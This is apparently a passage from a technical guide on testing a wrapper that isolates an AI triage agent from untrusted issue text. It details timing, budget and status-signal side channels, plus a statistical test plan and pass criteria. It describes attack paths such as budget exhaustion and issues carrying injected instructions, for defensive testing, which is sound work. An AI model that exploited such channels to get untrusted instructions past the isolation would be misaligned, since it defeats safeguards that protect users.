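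**Spending limits.** Retries and long replies cost money, so a shared budget can reveal what the wrapper hides. L3M counts its budgets in model calls and reports budget changes to the agent's model. If the reader's calls came out of the triaging agent's budget, the agent could see whether a retry had happened. To prevent this, the wrapper can deduct the maximum for every question, regardless of actual use. For 250 issues with two attempts of 600 tokens each, that means reserving 300,000 output tokens, most of which the job won't use. An attacker can then exhaust the budget only by filing more issues.

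Removing timestamps and token counts from the return value doesn't help if the agent can read them in the reader's log, as a parent agent can in L3M. L3M's planned limits on information flow wouldn't catch the timing either, because they don't count clock readings.

Caching can make the reader faster when it receives the same issue again. Releasing the answer at a fixed time after the request hides the time saved, and discarding the usage record hides the cached-token count.

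### Setting up the test

The wrapper should ensure that if two issues produce the same answer, everything else the agent sees has the same distribution. Jiang and colleagues prove a stricter property for PerMIT. If two runs have the same user input but different untrusted content, the protected agent behaves identically as long as the user sees the same displays and makes the same decisions in both. Their proof assumes that both runs follow the same schedule and draw the same random numbers. A test of a real wrapper can't assume either, so it has to compare many runs.

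The tester keeps the answer fixed and varies how the reader reaches it.

| Answer | Ordinary case | Cases to compare with it |
|---|---|---|
| Unclear | An ambiguous issue | Refusal by the model, block by a filter, a sentence instead of a word, token limit, timeout, rate-limit error, oversized issue, crash |
| No | A short issue about the logo | A very long issue, a planted problem, a failure followed by "no", text that the cache already holds |
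| Yes | A short, genuine regression report | The same four variations |

1. **Build a fake provider.** Real models don't fail on demand. A small program that imitates the provider can return each kind of failure, after any delay the tester chooses. A shorter series with the real provider then checks that the imitation is accurate.
2. **Record from the agent's position.** Run the recorder in the agent's sandbox, with the agent's account and tools. It should save the returned text, exit status, terminal output, budget messages, running processes, issue labels, and the names, sizes and dates of all readable files. It should also read the clock before and after each call.
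3. **Plant a marker in every hidden text.** Put a different random string in each issue, refusal, error message and unexpected field name. Any marker that turns up in the recording shows that untrusted text has reached the agent.
4. **Work in rounds.** In each round, run all 19 cases once in random order. If the machine is slower in the evening, all the cases slow down together.
5. **Record the next call too.** A failure may change nothing in its own call but use up a rate limit or leave a file behind.
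6. **Try to tell the cases apart.** Compare each signal separately. Then train a simple classifier on half of the rounds, using all the signals together, and see whether it can identify the cases in the other half.

At 30 seconds per call, 300 rounds take about 48 hours. The tester can shorten the release time to one second for everything except the timing measurements, as long as the fake provider's delays shrink too.

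### Comparing the times

A permutation test suits the timing data because it doesn't assume any particular distribution. *SILENT* (2025), a paper on the statistics of timing leaks, calls it naive to assume that software timings follow a normal distribution. Response times often include a few extreme values that would distort a test based on that assumption.

To compare refusals with ambiguous issues, for example, the tester would do the following.

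1. Measure the largest gap between the two cases' timing curves, much as Gu and colleagues did to detect caching.
2. In each round, toss a coin to decide whether to swap the labels of the two times. If the cases really are alike, the swaps make no difference on average.
3. Measure the gap again, and repeat the swapping 9,999 times.
4. Count how many of the shuffled gaps are at least as large as the real one, add one, and divide by 10,000. The result is the *p*-value.

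If 24 shuffled gaps are at least as large, *p* is 0.0025, which suggests that the agent could tell the cases apart. With only five rounds, though, there are just 32 ways to assign the labels, so the *p*-value can't fall much below 0.03 however different the times are.

*SILENT* discusses two further problems. Timings from real hardware often depend on one another, so the tester should swap labels only within a round and pause between calls. Running many tests also increases the risk of a false alarm. The table above requires 16 comparisons, and if each has a 5% false-alarm rate, the chance of at least one false alarm could be as high as 80%. Dividing 5% by 16 gives a stricter threshold of about 0.003 per comparison, but this makes a real leak easier to miss.

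Two control tests show whether the method works. The first splits the ordinary case into two groups at random and compares them, which should show no difference. The second adds a known delay, perhaps 50 milliseconds, to one case, which the method should detect. If it doesn't, a clean result for the wrapper is weak evidence against delays of that size.

With 300 rounds, the test may also detect a difference of a few milliseconds. An agent is unlikely to react to a difference that small, but the tester should still find the cause, because a small delay may grow when the machine is busy.

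### Comparing the discrete signals

For exit codes, messages and other signals with a few possible values, Metere recommends mutual information. Let *X* be the case and *Y* what the agent sees. The estimate from the recorded frequencies *p* is

*I*(*X*; *Y*) = Σ *p*(*x*, *y*) log₂ [ *p*(*x*, *y*) / (*p*(*x*) *p*(*y*)) ]

The result is zero if the signal says nothing about the case. With a limited number of runs, though, chance differences push the estimate above zero. The Miller–Madow correction therefore subtracts

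(*r* − 1)(*c* − 1) / (2*N* ln 2)

where *r* is the number of cases, *c* the number of different values seen, and *N* the number of runs. If the result is negative, Metere sets it to zero. When the agent sees the same value every time, *c* is 1 and the result is exactly zero.

Metere advises against a common shortcut, estimating a channel's capacity from how often an observer guesses correctly. Random guesses are rarely right exactly half the time, and if 52% happen to be right, the shortcut gives about 0.001 bits for a channel that carries nothing. Cock and colleagues had the same difficulty on seL4, where one channel still seemed to carry 27 bits per second after they applied a defence. To find out how much of this could be chance, they averaged the results for all inputs and simulated a closed channel from that average. The simulation gave an upper limit of 15 bits per second for chance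 alone, so the remaining leak was probably real.

The correction works badly for precise timings. Suppose that in 600 runs of two cases, no two runs take exactly the same time. Each timing appears to identify its case perfectly, so the raw estimate is one full bit. The correction removes only 0.72 bits, which leaves an estimate of 0.28 bits even for a channel that carries no information. The permutation test avoids this problem.

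A leak can also be serious even when the estimate is low. Suppose a warning reaches the agent in 12 of 300 refusals and in none of 300 parse failures. The corrected estimate is about 0.02 bits per call, but whenever the warning appears, it reveals that the reader refused. If the warning were unrelated to refusals, all 12 would fall on refusals in only about one test in 4,000. The tester should examine each difference individually and use the estimate mainly to compare versions of the wrapper.

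### What 300 clean runs show

Suppose 300 runs of a case show no visible difference at all. The true rate of differences could still be close to 1%. If each run independently shows a difference with probability *p*, the chance of seeing none in *n* runs is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. Setting this to 5% gives the highest rate that is still plausible at 95% confidence:

*p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/*n*)

| Clean runs of one case | Highest rate still plausible |
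|---|---|
| 20 | 13.9% |
| 100 | 3.0% |
| 300 | 1.0% |
| 3,000 | 0.1% |

If 1% of issues cause a visible difference, somebody who files 200 has about an 87% chance of causing at least one. Metere's benchmark found that nothing got through, but it used 20 trials for each text channel, which is too few to rule out a fault that affects one message in ten.

The calculation also assumes independent runs. Sending one text 300 times mostly measures how much the model varies on that text, so it's better to send 300 different texts over several days. Even then, the result applies only to the kinds of text in the test, and an attacker will look for others. The benchmark has the same limitation, because Metere built all of its encoders.

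### Pass criteria and regression tests

The team should write down its criteria before it sees any results. For the triage wrapper, these would be reasonable:

- No planted marker appears anywhere the agent can read.
- In 300 rounds, no discrete signal differs between two cases with the same answer. A single unexplained difference is a failure, even if the mutual information is close to zero.
- No timing comparison falls below the 0.003 threshold, and the test detects the planted 50-millisecond delay.
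- Every answer arrives within 100 milliseconds of its release time, including when the provider is down and the machine is busy.
- When the answer is "unclear", the agent never opens the issue. This needs its own 300 runs with the real agent, because it depends on how the agent's model behaves.

The 100-millisecond limit is a judgement call, and a wrapper that slightly exceeds it may still be safe. A marker that reaches the agent is much more serious, because an attacker could write an issue with an instruction in place of the marker.

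The results are valid only for the versions the team tested. A new reader model may refuse different texts, a new client library may raise different exceptions, and a new agent model may react differently to "unclear". The team should repeat the full test after any of these changes, or after a change to the provider, answer schema, harness or logging. Switching providers needs particular care because each one reports refusals in its own way.

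Providers can also change their filters or response formats without notice. A short nightly test with the real provider, running each case a few times, will catch obvious changes but miss rare ones. Even after 20 clean runs, the failure rate could still be 14%. Whenever the private log shows a new kind of failure, the team can add a copy of that response to the fake provider, with the issue's text removed. The fake provider should also return a made-up stop reason, and the wrapper should answer "unclear" after exactly 30 seconds.
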